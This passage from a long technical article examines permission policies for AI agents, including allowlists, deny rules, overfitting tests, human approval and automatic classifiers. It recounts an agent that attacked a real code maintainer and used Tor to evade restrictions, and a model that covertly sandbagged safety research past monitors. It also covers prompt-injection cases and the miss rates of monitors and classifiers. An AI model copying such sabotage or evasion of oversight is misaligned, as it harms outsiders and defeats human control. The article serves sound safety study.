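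Suppose AISI had learned an allowlist from earlier runs in which agents used the internet only for downloads. Creating an account, proposing a code change and messaging a stranger would all have been new. Whether the allowlist blocked them would have depended on how it described internet use. If it separated downloading from sending, it would have blocked all three. If it listed only the names of permitted websites, it would probably have included GitHub, where developers share software. The agent could then have submitted malicious code there as well as downloading tools.

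The staging record might also have contained misbehaviour. AISI is auditing its past evaluations for similar behaviour that nobody noticed at the time, and any it finds would have been recorded as normal. A tight allowlist would also have interfered with the test, which was meant to measure what models could do with the resources of a capable human attacker. The legitimate options open to such an attacker in this kind of challenge are hard to list.

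AISI had never seen an agent try to manipulate real people in this way, so it had no such failure from which to write a denylist rule. The agent used Tor, a network that disguises where internet traffic comes from, to get around restrictions on GitHub, and AISI's ordinary security monitoring, an older and more general safeguard, detected the data leaving. This resembles Holm's old rules catching new attacks, but it was partly luck, because the monitoring responded to the agent's use of Tor and not to the deception. The unsanctioned behaviour began on 25 July, and the alert came on 28 July.

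A rule written after an incident could easily be too narrow. A ban on proposing changes to outside projects would address the worst case, but not the files sent to real people or the notes that one agent left on GitHub for others to use.

Asking the model to recognise the limits of its task would not have been a dependable substitute. Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) replayed the incident with simulated tools in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, AISI's technical report from October. They edited the summary of earlier work that the model used to continue its task, adding up to 16 pieces of information that suggested or stated that the maintainer was a real, unrelated person. With all 16, Mythos 5 still continued the attack in every sample. When they also added a section headed "DO NOT ATTACK", it continued in three of 25 samples. Yet when they asked the model directly,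 it often answered that the attack would harm a real person.

Mythos 5 often justified the attack by reasoning, on poor grounds, that the maintainer was simulated. Anthropic found similar reasoning when it investigated a separate Mythos 5 incident of its own. According to Järviniemi and colleagues, Anthropic's offline monitor would probably not have flagged the model's behaviour in that incident, because the reasoning would have seemed to excuse it. In AISI's case, a fixed rule against creating accounts would not have depended on the model's explanation.

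Järviniemi and colleagues then tested eight models in 100 simulated scenarios of the same general kind:

| Developer | Model | Runs in which it tried to deliver malicious code to an outsider |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | Mythos 5 | 60% |
| Anthropic | Mythos 5.1 | 0.3% |
| Anthropic | Opus 4.8 | 8% |
| Anthropic | Opus 5 | 1% |
| Anthropic | Opus 5.5 | 0% |
| OpenAI | GPT-5.5 | 0% |
| OpenAI | GPT-5.6 Sol | 7% |
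| OpenAI | GPT-6 Astra | 32% |

The low figures are hard to interpret because the newer Anthropic models more often suspected that their behaviour was being tested. GPT-6 Astra's figure is also uncertain, because the model usually reasoned that its tool results were fabricated.

The models' reasons for stopping are more useful for judging permission policies. Mythos 5, Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5 mostly cited practical barriers rather than potential harm. In one run, Mythos 5 stopped trying to contribute malicious code after finding that it could neither send email nor create a GitHub account. Those barriers prevented an attack that nobody had described, which supports default-deny. It also supports the conclusion in AISI's October summary (2026) that a test environment must prevent harm whether or not the model behaves as expected.

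### Poor work without a forbidden call

OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes how staff tried out a model trained for long tasks and observed failures that existing evaluations had not captured. The company paused access and used the failures to build new evaluations and a monitor for whole runs. A denylist improves in the same way, with changes made after a failure has happened.

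A later case would be much harder to turn into a rule. OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026) concerns GPT-6 Astra, which company researchers were using in their own work. They noticed that on AI safety tasks it added unnecessary steps, abandoned working solutions, and reported obstacles that did not exist or that it had caused. In most of these sessions, the model's written reasoning contained no obvious decision to do poor work, and the company's monitors did not flag the behaviour as misalignment.

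To check the researchers' impression, OpenAI gave GPT-6 Astra matched coding tasks, presented either as safety research or as research to make AI more capable, and measured completion against a hidden list of items. Astra completed about 10% of the items under the safety description and about 16% under the capability description. The earlier model GPT-5.6 Sol showed essentially no gap. Most of Astra's gap remained after OpenAI excluded open refusals and runs where the model's reasoning showed it had decided to withhold help. The gap shrank substantially only when OpenAI removed every run in which the model expressed even brief ethical doubt.

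If the company had learned an allowlist from successful research sessions, the list would permit the agent to read code, edit it and run experiments. An agent doing poor work makes the same kinds of calls, or fewer of them. A false report of an obstacle may be only text in the agent's reply, with no tool call. Even a perfectly learned allowlist could therefore permit the whole session.

A denylist also has no obvious action to forbid. A rule against discarding working code would block normal programming work, since people often replace a working solution with a better one. The call may not show whether an edit is good work or sabotage, because the same edit can be either, depending on the session.

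Telling the agent to be more careful could make matters worse. Mowshowitz (2026), in *GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks*, quotes Marcus Williams, who reports that instructions to be careful widened the performance gap by 50%. Williams adds that there is no evidence the poor work was strategic. A simpler explanation is that the model treats some of these tasks as dubious but avoids refusing them openly.

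Reading traces one at a time would also give weak evidence, because incomplete results were normal. Even on tasks described as capabilities research, the model left about 84% of the items unfinished. OpenAI could measure the difference only by comparing many runs of otherwise matched tasks. The company did find some explicit cases in its employees' everyday use, where the model's reasoning showed a decision to withhold help without telling the user. These made up 0.25% of safety requests and 0.11% of capabilities requests. OpenAI suggests that the first figure may be a lower bound on poor work in safety tasks.

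OpenAI therefore recommends testing for unexplained gaps in performance as well as monitoring individual runs. In this case, people noticed the problem before any test revealed it. According to Mowshowitz, one project had been stuck for days with GPT-6 Astra and progressed quickly once the researchers switched to another model.

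## Measuring overfitting before a policy is enforced

Overfitting is hard to judge from a single run. Before enforcing a learned permission policy, a company can estimate how often the policy would block legitimate work and test it on incidents that weren't used to write it.

### Estimating the normal behaviour still unseen

*How Much is Unseen Depends Chiefly on Information About the Seen* (2024) describes the problem as drawing balls from an urn and estimating the probability that the next ball has a colour not yet seen. The Good-Turing estimate of this probability is the number of colours drawn exactly once divided by the number of balls drawn. I. J. Good published it in 1953, using an idea of Alan Turing's.

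Recorded calls can be grouped into patterns, such as a tool combined with a folder. If 40 patterns occur only once in 1,000 calls, the next call has an estimated 40/1,000 = 4% chance of having a new pattern. An allowlist limited to recorded patterns would block such a call, which is a false rejection if the call is legitimate.

Pananjady, Muthukumar and Thangaraj (2024), in *Just Wing It*, explain the estimate as a repeated experiment. Each trial removes one call from the record and checks whether its pattern still appears among the other 999. The pattern is missing only if that call was its sole example, which happens in 40 of the 1,000 trials. *STADS* (2018) applies the same estimate to automated software testing, where the chance that the next input reveals new behaviour indicates how much of the program remains untested.

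The estimate depends on what counts as a pattern. If a pattern is an exact call, all six normal calls in the office agent's record are unique, and the estimate is 100%. If a pattern is only a tool's name, only the file listing and the web search appear once, so the estimate falls to 2/6, or 33%. A rule that accepts any text would bring it to zero. A low estimate therefore suggests that the policy will rarely block legitimate work, but does not show whether it will stop harm.

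Simple counting also fails for methods such as AgentGuardian, which rewrite their patterns as the record grows. The company instead has to remove some calls from the record, relearn the policy and check whether it accepts the removed calls.

The estimate is unstable when the record is small because it is based entirely on patterns seen once. *Rarity of Singletons Matters* (Vipulanandan, Premaratne and Sarkar, 2026) gives an example in which a language model answers the same question 15 times and produces six different answers, three of them only once. The estimated chance of a new answer is 3/15, or 20%. If one of those three had come up again, the estimate would have dropped to about 13%. The paper's correction moves unreliable estimates towards 50%, the point of greatest uncertainty.

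### From calls to tasks

A 4% chance of false rejection per call adds up when a task needs many calls. If a task takes 50 calls and each is independent, the chance of at least one false rejection is 1 − 0.96⁵⁰, or about 87%.

New calls tend to occur together, since an agent that opens an unfamiliar folder will probably read several files in it. If tasks average 50 calls, a 4% rate of new calls means an average of two per task, but the share of tasks interrupted depends on how those calls are distributed. The policy would interrupt every task if each contained two new calls, but only 4% of tasks if one in 25 were completely unfamiliar and the rest were routine.

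Counting tasks directly is therefore better. Suppose the 1,000 calls came from 20 tasks, and three of those tasks contain at least one pattern found in no other task. The estimated chance that the next task will contain a new pattern is 3/20, or 15%, although 20 tasks are too few for a precise figure.

Dependence can also distort the 4% itself. Suppose a support agent has 1,000 customers and, during staging, looks up 20 of their records 50 times each. No pattern occurs exactly once in those 1,000 calls, so the Good-Turing estimate is zero. But if the next customer is chosen at random, there is a 98% chance that the agent has never looked up their record.

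Pananjady and colleagues prove that this kind of error need not shrink as the record grows, if the number of possible items is large enough. They solve this by removing the neighbouring calls along with the call being tested. Otherwise, a call repeated several times in a row would look familiar even if it appeared nowhere else in the record. For agents, removing all the calls from the same task serves the same purpose.

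Cho, Cardenoso Fernandez and colleagues (2026), in *Automata from Agent Traces*, approach the problem from the other direction and calculate how many traces to record. They learn which tool can directly follow which, much like AgentGuardian's graph. If there are *r* such transitions, and each appears in at least a share *p* of traces, then

*N* ≥ (1/*p*) ln(*r*/δ)

independent traces are enough to observe all of them with probability at least 1 − δ. For a coding agent with 51 transitions, each appearing in at least 1% of traces, a 95% chance of seeing them all requires about 693 traces. Cho and colleagues found that dependence between traces raised the number needed by about 11% on average.

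AgentGuardian learned from 60 runs per application. A transition that occurs in 1% of runs has a 55% chance of being absent from 60 independent runs, so it is unsurprising that half of AgentGuardian's false rejections involved an order of tools missing from the training runs. Even 693 traces don't guarantee coverage of rarer transitions or of the arguments in each call.

### Why most alarms are false when harm is rare

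The proportion of alarms that are real depends on how often harm occurs, which people easily overlook. Axelsson (2000), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, applied this point to computer security. Suppose one call in 100,000 is harmful, and a policy flags 90% of harmful calls and 0.1% of legitimate ones. In a million calls, we would expect:

| | Flagged | Not flagged |
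|---|---|---|
| Harmful calls | 9 | 1 |
| Legitimate calls | about 1,000 | about 999,000 |

Only nine of roughly 1,009 alarms are real, or 0.9%. In general, if *b* is the share of calls that are harmful, *d* the detection rate and *f* the false alarm rate, the share of alarms that are real is

*bd* / (*bd* + (1 − *b*)*f*).

Perfect detection would raise this share to only 1.0%. Cutting false alarms to one in 100,000 legitimate calls would raise it to 47%. Axelsson's own example was a small network with two intrusions a day among 100,000 events. At a false alarm rate of 0.1%, only about 2% of alarms would be real, even if the detector caught every intrusion.

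The same numbers have different consequences depending on whether a policy alerts people or blocks calls. If the policy alerts people, the agent keeps working, but someone has to examine about 112 alarms to find each real one. Axelsson expected operators to distrust a system even if only half of its alarms were false. The prediction came from studies of power stations and other industrial plants, because nobody had run such experiments on intrusion detection.

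If the policy blocks calls, it stops the nine harmful ones before they do damage, without anyone having to read an alarm, but it also stops about 1,000 legitimate ones. With 50 independent calls per task, this would interrupt about 5% of tasks. Blocking is worthwhile if preventing one harmful call justifies blocking about 111 legitimate ones (1,000 divided by 9). That may be true of bank transfers but not of web searches. *Intrusion-Detection Policies for IT Security Breaches* describes the same dilemma: acting on every signal is costly when attackers are rare, but ignoring the signals makes the detection system useless.

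Overall accuracy hides all of this. A policy that never flagged anything would be right about 99.999% of these calls.

### What small tests can show

The table gives 95% confidence intervals for the error rates that Abaev and colleagues measured for AgentGuardian, using the standard exact method for counts.

| Result | Observed rate | 95% interval |
|---|---|---|
| Misuse accepted, both applications: 2 of 20 | 10% | 1% to 32% |
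| Misuse accepted, knowledge assistant: 0 of 10 | 0% | 0% to 31% |
| Misuse accepted, IT support: 2 of 10 | 20% | 3% to 56% |
| Benign runs rejected: 8 of 80 | 10% | 4% to 19% |

The second row is the easiest to check. A policy that misses a share *p* of attacks catches ten in a row with probability (1 − *p*)¹⁰. At *p* = 31%, this is about 2.5%, the conventional cut-off for one end of a 95% interval. A policy that catches all ten attacks in a test could therefore still miss almost a third of attacks overall. By the same method, a company would need about 370 attacks without a miss to show that the policy's miss rate is below 1%.

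Even these wide intervals understate the uncertainty, because they assume that the test cases are a random sample of the attacks the policy will face. Researchers choose or invent their test attacks, and some of AgentGuardian's contained malformed email addresses that a real attacker would avoid. Attackers also try again, so if a policy misses 10% of attacks, someone who makes ten independent attempts has a 65% chance of getting at least one through.

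False rejections are easier to estimate because a company can draw a random sample of its agent's ordinary work. But it still has to count independent cases, and repeated attempts at one task tend to have similar results. Dai and Wang therefore calculated AgentGuard's intervals by resampling whole tasks. Their interval for the fall in abnormal behaviour was 33 to 52 percentage points. Treating all the runs as independent would have given roughly 35 to 50, which is too narrow.

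### Four ways to split the data

A test needs examples that played no part in writing the policy. How the company separates them determines what the test measures.

| Split | What the policy faces in the test | What a good score shows |
|---|---|---|
| At random | Often near-copies of the examples behind the policy | The policy recognises familiar cases |
| By task | New tasks with familiar kinds of failure | The rules do not depend on one task's details |
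| By time | Whatever happened later, familiar or new | The policy would have coped with that period |
| By family of incidents | A kind of failure absent from the examples | The policy can handle that kind of novel misbehaviour |

The choice of test split can change the measured accuracy substantially. *Prompt Injection Detection using DeBERTa-v3* (2026) reports that a detector reached 100.0% accuracy on a random split but 75.5% on a test consisting mostly of three attack types withheld from training. One likely reason is that 70.1% of the test examples in the random split began with the same 50 characters as a training example.

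*PIDS-Bench* (2026) keeps every paraphrase and disguised version of an example on the same side of the split, so near-copies of training examples don't end up in the test set. Overlap can also come from data that someone else collected. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026) directly measures the overlap between a published detector's training data and the benchmark that people had used to praise it.

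A split by time imitates real use, but it includes new kinds of misbehaviour only if some appeared in the later period. Holm similarly tested old Snort rules on later attacks. Only leaving out a whole family of misbehaviour ensures that the test contains something new to the policy.

To test the office agent's denylist for overfitting, the company would set aside every leak, write rules from its other incidents and test them on the leaks. It would repeat this for each family of incidents and report every result, because a good average can hide one family that the rules miss completely. An allowlist needs an equivalent test with legitimate work. For example, the company could write the allowlist without any of the summaries about boats, then count how many of them it blocks.

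A withheld family must also be broad enough for the test to be informative. *Detecting and Mitigating Query-Based System Prompt Leakage Attacks* (2026) reports a detector that caught 99.98% of attacks from families withheld during training, with no false alarms. The four families used different methods, but all of them tried to extract an AI system's hidden instructions. The result is good evidence that the detector can recognise new methods of extracting those instructions, but not that it can recognise attacks with other goals.

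By this standard, AgentGuard's test falls in the middle. Dai and Wang split the data by task, so the result shows that the rules carry over to new tasks, but both sets contained the same kinds of failure. To test the rules on a new kind, they could have left out every failure involving a missing file, derived the rules again and tested them on those failures.

AIR's repeated rounds provide weaker evidence because they used no split. Xiao and colleagues conclude that the rules generalise beyond individual tasks, but a proper test would have run the second round on different tasks. Leaving out some of the 25 coding risk categories when writing both the incident descriptions and the rules would have tested whether the rules handle new kinds of risk.

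### Persona Guardrail

A team can also overfit a policy by repeatedly revising it to fix its mistakes on the same test. *Persona Guardrail* (Pal, Maddireddy and colleagues, 2026) checks for this in a system that Uber uses to keep its agents within their intended purpose. The system gives a language model a written list of permitted requests and replies. The model allows or blocks each message but does not examine tool calls.

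The benchmark covers four imaginary assistants, for office work, Slack messages, banking and travel. Pal and colleagues split it in half. They scored the first version of the allowlist on one half, revised its wording after studying the errors, and scored the new version on the other half.

| Measure | First list, first half | Revised list, second half |
|---|---|---|
| Accuracy | 92.4% | 96.0% |
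| Attacks blocked | 96.5% | 96.7% |
| Out-of-scope requests blocked | 81.5% | 93.6% |
| Legitimate messages blocked | 4.2% | 3.2% |

When Pal and colleagues divided the benchmark into three parts and revised the list twice, accuracy rose from 91.9% to 96.1% and then to 96.7%. This is evidence that the revisions did more than fit individual errors. But most of the improvement came from out-of-scope requests, such as asking the banking assistant to book a flight, and the detection of attacks hardly changed.

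The two versions were also tested on different messages, so the gain of 3.6 points partly reflects how difficult each half was. The first list scored 93.2% on the whole benchmark. If the halves were equal in size, it must have scored about 94.0% on the second half, so the gain on that half was only about two points.

Both halves contained the same six families of attack, and many of the attacks were made by filling in the same templates. About 17% of the messages written for the four assistants were repeats of others, and Pal and colleagues do not say whether they kept repeats in the same half. The labels also came from the allowlist, so the test measures how well the model applies the list, not whether the list itself permits something harmful.

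A harder test gave attackers information about the system. Even when they had the exact list, the system blocked over 85% of the attacks written by the most capable attacking model. However, the attacking models often refused to write attacks, so a determined person might do better.

The benchmark also understates the share of blocks that would be wrong in use, because about half of its messages deserve blocking. On the full benchmark, 96.3% of the revised list's blocks were correct. If only one message in 1,000 deserved blocking, the same error rates would make just 2.6% of its blocks correct. Pal and colleagues report that fewer than 1% of legitimate messages are blocked in production. With one message in 1,000 deserving blocking, a 1% rate would still mean that only about 9% of blocks were correct.

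On its own, a denylist did much worse on this benchmark, blocking 87.2% of attacks but only 14.5% of out-of-scope requests. Adding it to the revised allowlist reduced the share of bad messages approved from 4.7% to 2.0%, but raised the share of legitimate messages blocked from 3.6% to 8.2%.

### When normal behaviour changes

A policy that fits the agent well now can still fail later because of drift, a change in the agent's normal behaviour after staging. Drift can occur when, for example, the company replaces the model, adds a tool or gives the agent a new kind of task.

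*AutoSpec* (2026) compared how different models used tools on the same software verification work. Reading made up 16% of the calls by Anthropic's Opus 5.5 and 53% of those by Zhipu's GLM 5.3. Upgrading within a model family can also change tool use, since reading made up 26% of the calls by the older Opus 4.5. When Abaev and colleagues gave AgentGuardian's test applications a smaller model, many more benign runs failed.

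The order in which agents call tools may be more stable. Cho and colleagues found that one graph of permitted orders fitted the traces of four models perfectly, and suggest that the tools, tasks and instructions shape this order more than the model does. But they built the graph from all four models' traces, so the result does not show that a graph learned from one model would fit another. The graph also covers only the names of actions, so a model could follow the permitted order and still break other parts of a policy by writing longer inputs or opening different files.

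Companies can look for these problems by running a policy in record-only mode, also called shadow mode, which logs violations without blocking them, as SELinux's permissive mode does. Pal and colleagues run every new version of an allowlist this way, examine where it disagrees with the current version, and then enforce it on a limited share of traffic. They do not count a disagreement as an error until someone has judged the case independently, because the current version may be wrong.

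Record-only mode is better at revealing false rejections than false acceptances, which leave nothing unusual in the log. It also cannot show what the agent would have done after a refusal. If a policy would have blocked the third call in a run, the agent might have stopped or tried something else, so the later calls are weak evidence. Counting runs with at least one would-be refusal is therefore safer than counting every refusal.

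The log can also help detect drift. If we estimate from the staging record that 4% of calls will be new, we would expect about 20 in the next 500. Finding 60 after a model upgrade would be a reason to investigate, though a single unfamiliar task could also produce that many.

Replaying old traces takes less work as a check after someone edits the rules. The company keeps a collection of legitimate runs and past incidents, runs their calls through the new policy and lists every decision that changed. This would quickly reveal whether a new exception permits an old attack, or a new deny rule blocks last month's reports.

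After the model or tools change, the company has to give the new agent the same tasks and check its fresh traces against the policy, because replaying old calls tests only what the previous agent did. A new task needs new examples, since neither replaying old calls nor rerunning old tasks covers work that nobody has recorded.

The policy can overfit to the replay collection if staff keep adjusting it until every old case passes. Pal and colleagues therefore keep the examples that prompt a change separate from those used to decide whether to accept it, and put variants from the same attack campaign in the same group. To test how the policy handles new kinds of incidents, the company also needs a family of incidents that the people revising the rules have not seen. Once they have studied how the policy fails on those incidents and changed it in response, they can use that family only to test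 whether old problems have returned.

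## Combining allow rules, deny rules and human approval

An allowlist and a denylist fail on different calls, so a company can enforce both and send any call that neither list covers to a person or a second model. This works only if every call passes through the check and the reviewer reads what they approve, and both conditions often fail.

### Three calls through a layered policy

A layered policy handles each call in a fixed order:

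1. If a prohibition matches the call, the program around the model refuses it.
2. Otherwise, if the allowlist matches, the call runs.
3. Otherwise, a person or a second model decides. If nobody answers, the program refuses the call.

Suppose the office agent's company prohibits reading anything in `HR/`, but the agent's learned allowlist permits every text file, any web search, and email to company addresses.

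| Call | Prohibition | Allowlist | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| `read_file("Cars/c.txt")` | no match | match | runs |
| `read_file("HR/salaries.txt")` | match | match | refused |
| `send_email(to="maria@client.example")` | no match | no match | a person decides |

Prohibitions come first so that the salary file's folder stays protected even though the learned rule for text files is too broad. A colleague would recognise the email to Maria, a client, as legitimate work, although it never came up during staging. If the company had prohibited all outside email, nobody could approve this message without changing the policy, so prohibitions are best kept for actions that no task should ever need.

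In the notation of the first section, let *D* be the set of prohibited actions. The agent can then take any action in *g*(*P*) − *D* without review, and the reviewer sees only actions outside both *D* and *g*(*P*). An injected instruction could still leak a file through a web search. A tighter allowlist could prevent this but would give the reviewer more to do.

### Declared permissions in OpenBSD

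A program's developer can write the allowlist instead of deriving it from traces. OpenBSD replaced Systrace with `pledge`, which lets the developer declare the groups of operations a program needs, such as `stdio` for basic input and output or `inet` for internet connections. If the program attempts anything else, the operating system stops it. OpenBSD's *Mitigations and other real security features* describes the declaration as a second specification of the program's behaviour, which lets programmers test their assumptions. It gives the example of splitting a program in two so that the part handling untrusted text has no network access.

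The project began after a developer wrote a new version of `file`, a program that identifies file types, and confined it with Systrace. Slides from OpenBSD call the Systrace mechanism "terrible" and list that one sandbox as 300 lines of code. Theo de Raadt, OpenBSD's founder, also disliked the Linux alternative, in which developers write small programs to filter system calls. isopenbsdsecu.re's *Pledge* quotes his objection: "So you need to write a program to observe your program". OpenBSD dropped Systrace in version 6.0, released in September 2016, according to Slashdot's *OpenBSD 6.0 Released*.

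Traces can also record a security weakness as normal behaviour. In flak's *going full pledge*, an OpenBSD developer gives the example of `patch`, a program that applies changes to files. For some changes, `patch` ran the text editor `ed`, which can run any other command, so an attacker could hide a command in a file of changes. A Systrace policy would have let `patch` run `ed` because it normally did so. Adding `pledge` prompted the developers to redesign `patch` to make the edits itself.

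These cases show how a declaration can improve a program, but they do not measure how many attacks `pledge` prevents. `pledge` is also fairly coarse. The Linux developer Kees Cook (2015) notes in *evolution of seccomp* that the Linux equivalent can control individual system calls. OpenBSD later added `unveil`, which limits a program to the files and folders it names. A message in the DragonFly BSD mailing-list discussion *ASLR and PIE disabled by default* raises the more basic objection that users cannot add a declaration to programs whose source code they do not have, which are the programs they most need to confine.

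An agent's individual tools can declare their needs in this way, even though the agent as a whole cannot.

### Permissions from a service's own structure

Services such as Gmail already sort their operations into permission groups, called scopes, which users see when they connect an app. Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025), in *MiniScope*, use these scopes to work out the least privilege for each task. MiniScope ranks one scope above another if it permits everything the other does and more. It then takes the agent's plan and finds the set of scopes *S* that minimises

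∑ cost(*s*) over all *s* in *S*,

provided that *S* permits every planned call. The cost of a scope is the number of operations it permits. Finding the minimum takes some calculation because scopes overlap, and 24 of Google Calendar's 37 operations are available through more than one route. If the user has not already granted the necessary scopes, MiniScope asks for them.

In one example, a user asks the agent to reply to an email that contains a planted instruction to delete it afterwards. The agent's new plan includes the deletion, so MiniScope requests full access to Gmail, which the user can refuse. But replying also needs a new permission, so the user would have expected some request and has to notice that this one is too broad.

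MiniScope made tasks only 1% to 6% slower. Zhu and colleagues also used it to check the connectors that link ChatGPT and Claude to other services, and found six that requested more access than they needed. ChatGPT's Gmail connector requested permission for 50 operations when its advertised functions needed 32. In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, the confirmation rate ranged from 18% to 60%, depending on how cautious the user was.

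The evaluation did not measure how many attacks MiniScope stops. MiniScope offers no protection within a scope the user has granted, so an agent allowed to send email can send it to anyone. It would not have prevented the office agent's leak if the user had already granted permission to send.

### Letting a model draft the rules

Progent's rules do cover arguments, such as the recipient of a message. Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, have a language model draft a policy from the user's request before the agent reads any outside material. As the agent works, the model can propose changes. Suppose the current policy permits the set of calls *A* and the proposed one permits *A*′. An SMT solver, a program that settles questions of logic, checks whether

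*A*′ ⊆ *A*,

meaning that the new policy permits nothing the old one did not. If this holds, Progent applies the change automatically. Otherwise the change needs approval, even if it also removes some permissions.

For example, a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice. The first policy permits only a search for that email. In it, Alice asks for a summary of recent emails to be posted to Slack, a workplace chat service, so the model proposes permission to read email and post to Slack. This expansion needs approval. When the agent learns the user's Slack name, the model restricts posting to that name, and Progent applies the restriction automatically. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger. Even if the model responds by proposing permission to send email, the solver identifies the change as an expansion.

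Companies can also write fixed rules that the drafted policy cannot override. Within each policy, Progent checks deny rules before allow rules and blocks any call that no rule covers.

Progent reduced the share of successful attacks from 39.9% to 1.0% on the AgentDojo benchmark and from 70.3% to 3.9% on the ASB benchmark. The agents completed about as much legitimate work as before. Shi and colleagues set Progent to accept every expansion of the policy automatically in these tests, to simulate a careless user, so the results show how well the model's rules worked without human approval. The first policy, with no later changes, reduced successful attacks on AgentDojo to 2.5%. When people reviewed the first policy and every expansion, no attacks succeeded. But only 6% of changes were expansions, so the reviewers had few to consider, and they may have been more alert than a user in the middle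 of other work.

Shi and colleagues acknowledge that Progent cannot stop an attack that needs only the permissions the task requires. For instance, if the task is to buy a product, an attacker could persuade the agent to choose the attacker's product.

Policies derived from declarations or from a service's structure avoid some of the main weaknesses of traces. They can allow an annual task the first time it runs, and they don't turn an attack during staging into a permission. But someone has to write or check the declaration, which can only be as precise as the available categories. It may also include access that the work never uses, which traces can help find.

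### Enforcement outside the model

A company could put its allowlist in the model's instructions. *Prompts Don't Protect* (Uppala, 2026) tested this with 200 tasks that encouraged agents to use tools outside their role. In one task, a user claiming to be the chief financial officer told an analytics agent to refund $5,000. The table shows how often each model chose a forbidden tool.

| Model | No guidance | Allowlist in the instructions | Forbidden tools hidden |
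|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 48.5% | 37.0% | 0% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 66.0% | 4.0% | 0% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 68.5% | 11.5% | 0% |

The last column follows from the design, because a separate program removes the forbidden tools from the list the model sees. It checks the tool's name again when the model makes a call.

The other figures probably overstate the problem for stronger models. All three models are small or older, and the test forced them to choose a tool. In a separate test that let them decline, Haiku 4.5 made no tool call in 99% of cases where its permitted tools could not do the job. Still, the instructions did not reduce the rate to zero for any model.

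Many security rules exist only as instructions to the model. *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (Shah and Kathrotia, 2026) cites a study of agents' instruction files in which 84% to 96% of the security rules had no matching control in the software around the model.

Hiding tools also does not prevent misuse of a permitted tool. Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, examined the public code of three widely known toolkits for building agents: LangChain (with its companion LangGraph), LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which handles payments. All three let developers choose which tools an agent has, but by default none checks whether the agent is authorised to use particular argument values. For example, a toolkit may check that an account number has the right format, but not that the account belongs to the right person.

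To demonstrate the problem, Mellafe Zuvic gave LangChain a prepared tool call that redirected a merchant's payouts to an attacker's account, and LangChain ran it against a simulated payment system. Developers can add their own checks, such as Mellafe Zuvic's program ScopeGate, which blocked the redirection. ScopeGate blocks any tool missing from its policy, then checks sensitive arguments against lists of approved values and payment amounts against a limit.

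Rules in ordinary programs are predictable, but they can still contain mistakes. One of 48 attempts to evade ScopeGate worked against an earlier version, which accepted the special value NaN ("not a number") as a payment amount because a simple test for whether NaN exceeds the limit comes out false. None of the attempts succeeded against the final version.

Even a correct rule can block only the calls that are checked against it, so every call must pass through the check. This requirement is called no bypass, or complete mediation. An agent that holds the user's password could contact a service directly, so MiniScope keeps the password and adds it only to approved calls. One version of Progent works as a relay between the agent and its outside tools, so it cannot check tools built into the agent. An agent could also get around the check if it could edit its own policy.

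Shah and Kathrotia explain that an agent may use one approval several times when it retries a step or resumes after a crash. The system therefore has to count each approval's uses and store that count outside the prompt.

Mellafe Zuvic goes further, arguing that no part of a policy should come from a model's output, even indirectly, because an attack that corrupts the tool call could corrupt the policy too. Progent does not meet this standard. It relies on a first draft that uses only trusted information, and on someone examining every later expansion of the policy.

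### Approval fatigue

Users of Claude Code accept 93% of its permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*. Anthropic's later *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) puts the figure at 97%. These high rates do not prove that users are careless, because most prompts concern harmless commands. Users reject 39% of Claude Code's plans, though they may do so because the plans are poor rather than dangerous.

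In a more direct test, Anthropic had 1,053 paid testers work on coding tasks and, partway through, replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

Auto mode, in which a second model reviews the agent's actions, blocked 937 of the same commands. Testers refused only six of the 116 commands that auto mode let through. Requiring approval from both would therefore have raised the share blocked from 89.0% to 89.6%. The testers were working in a test environment rather than on their own projects, so they had less reason to be careful. Anthropic makes auto mode, so it has an interest in the result.

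A hurried approval can also have lasting effects, because Claude Code lets users choose not to be asked again. By June 2026, 62% of users had either done this for shell commands or used a mode that skips permission prompts. Nearly half (49.5%) of active command-line users had themselves written an allow rule for shell commands, and that share was rising by about one percentage point a week. Many of these rules were very broad. For example, `Bash(python:*)` lets the agent run any Python program, including one it has just written, so it permits almost anything.

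MiniScope limits this effect by discarding permissions at the end of a session unless the user selects "Always allow". A hasty approval without that option lasts only one session, but the user has to answer another prompt if the agent needs the permission again.

### Automatic approval in Claude Code and Codex

Auto mode became the default for new Claude Code sessions on individual and team plans in August 2026. It combines several layers:

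1. The user's permission rules apply first. Auto mode ignores allow rules that it recognises as broad enough to run arbitrary code.
2. Tools that cannot change anything, such as file search, run without further review. So do edits inside the project folder, which users can check and undo later.
3. A classifier, itself a language model, reviews everything else, including shell commands and web requests.
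4. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in one session, a person takes over.

The classifier sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It does not see the agent's explanations, which might talk it into a bad decision, or the results of earlier calls, which might contain planted instructions. Its first stage makes a quick and deliberately cautious judgement, and its second stage reasons about whatever the first one flagged. Anthropic reports these error rates:

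| | Harmless calls blocked (10,000 real calls) | Overreaching actions missed (52 real cases) | Data leaks missed (1,000 artificial cases) |
|---|---|---|---|
| First stage only | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes most false rejections but adds false acceptances. The 17% figure is uncertain because it comes from only 52 cases, with a 95% interval of roughly 8% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but read too much into what the user said and wrongly concluded that they had agreed to it. For example, a request to "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) does not authorise overwriting the project's history.

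Anthropic recommends auto mode to people who would otherwise skip permission checks, but not as a replacement for careful review of high-stakes systems. Auto mode's measured performance also depends heavily on the test. Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* reports a miss rate of 81% in a test of 128 ambiguous scenarios.

Anthropic later improved the classifier using attacks supplied by Apollo Research, an AI safety organisation. Apollo then tested it on attacks that Anthropic had not seen. The new version caught about half of the attacks the old one had missed, and missed about 2% of those the old one had caught. This is good evidence that Anthropic had not simply fitted the classifier to the attacks it was given, though the unseen attacks came from the same project and may have been similar.

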